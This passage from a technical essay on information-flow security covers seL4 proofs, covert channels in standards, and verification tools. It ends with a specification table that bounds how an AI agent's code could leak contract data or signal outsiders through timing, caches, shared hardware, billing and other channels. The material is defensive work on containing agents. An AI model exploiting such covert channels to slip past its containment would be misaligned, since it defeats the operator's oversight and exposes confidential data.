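The spare copies close a channel that the proof uncovered. seL4 deletes an object when its last capability disappears, so a partition could have found out whether another partition still held a capability to an object by deleting its own. Klein, Andronick and colleagues later described another proof that the kernel's binary code correctly implements its C code, so that step no longer requires trusting the compiler.

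The proof doesn't cover timing channels, such as those through shared caches. A partition can also overrun its time slice by making a kernel call just before the slice ends, which delays the next partition. Murray and colleagues suggested refusing kernel calls near the end of each slice, but left the choice of remedy to whoever deploys the system.

Trying to prove that a system doesn't leak information can reveal covert channels in published standards too. *Reasoning About Information Flow Security of Separation Kernels with Channel-based Communication* (2015) reports one in the message queues of ARINC 653, a standard for aircraft operating systems, and in two open-source kernels. The paper fixes this in its model by letting the system lose messages, which improves secrecy but makes communication less reliable.

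Proof used to take too much work for most projects. The seL4 information-flow proof took about 51 person-months and built on an earlier correctness proof that took about 25 person-years. In *Nickel*, Sigurbjarnarson, Nelson and colleagues automated part of this kind of work with a tool that checks an interface against an information-flow policy and returns a counterexample when it finds a covert channel. The operator's publisher and ledger have small interfaces that might suit such a tool.

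Language models have further reduced the work that formal verification requires. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes how the company's model Claude proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. The proofs run to 180 million lines (Smith, *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs*, 2026). They rule out crashes, memory errors and failed assertions for inputs under 64 MB (EconoTimes, *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points*, 2026).

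Those properties concern one run at a time, so a library could satisfy them all and still leak secrets. But proving noninterference for a few small trusted objects now looks feasible. The operator would still have to decide which outputs to treat as visible to outsiders, because a proof can't cover an output that its model leaves out.

### The completed specification

The specification below assumes that the operator trusts the conversion company and the model provider with the contracts' text. The same provider runs the agent's own model. The operator's code converts the folder before the agent code starts, and all attempts finish before the same deadline. From the folder's 400 bits, the ledger deducts 360 for the published list and 4 for the rounded bill, which leaves 36.

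| Effect | Mechanism | Remaining bound | Test | What the operator has to trust |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reaching other files, services or programs | Grants only for the converted folder, the summary object and the metered model object | No access beyond these grants | Try other paths, hosts and global objects | Runtime, loader and granted objects |
| Telling outsiders about the contracts | Publisher with eight categories in a fixed order, and a ledger | 360 bits for the list, and 400 bits in total over the folder's lifetime | Submit malformed lists, make two charges at once and restart during a charge | Publisher, ledger and the ledger's storage |
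| Showing staff text from contracts they may not read | Labels on each section, and a new summary file only at the deadline | 1 bit per run, from whether a new file appears | Change only the Birch contract and compare what the sales team can read | Label-tracking runtime, initial labels and summary object |
| Signalling through the conversion service | Conversion in advance, with numbered jobs and a separate page quota | 0 bits from agent code, though delays may reveal document lengths to other customers | Check that the service receives no requests while agent code runs | Conversion company and the operator's code |
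| Signalling through the model provider's cache | A separate cache for the operator | 0 bits to other customers through the cache | Send matching prompts from a second account and time the replies | Model provider |
| Signalling through the time of publication | One deadline, and a guaranteed processor share for the operator's code | 0 bits if every release is on time | Compare release times after fast, slow and endless runs | Clock, scheduler and the operator's code |
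| Signalling through shared hardware | A machine that no other customer uses | 0 bits to other customers through that machine | Run a deliberate sender and try to receive its signal from another account | Hosting company |
| Spending tokens and money | One budget for all attempts, reservations before each call, and a reserve for cleanup | 1.5 million tokens plus the reserve | Retry endlessly, make three calls at once, pass negative amounts and drop replies | Meter, and the provider's token counts and prices |
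| Revealing token use through the bill | Rounding up to the next 100,000 tokens, with a flat charge for cleanup | 4 bits to accounts staff | Compare the bills from paired runs | Billing code |
| Occupying the processor or memory | Limits on the agent code's process | The processor and memory limits that the operator sets | Run an endless loop, a growing list and extra threads | Operating system |
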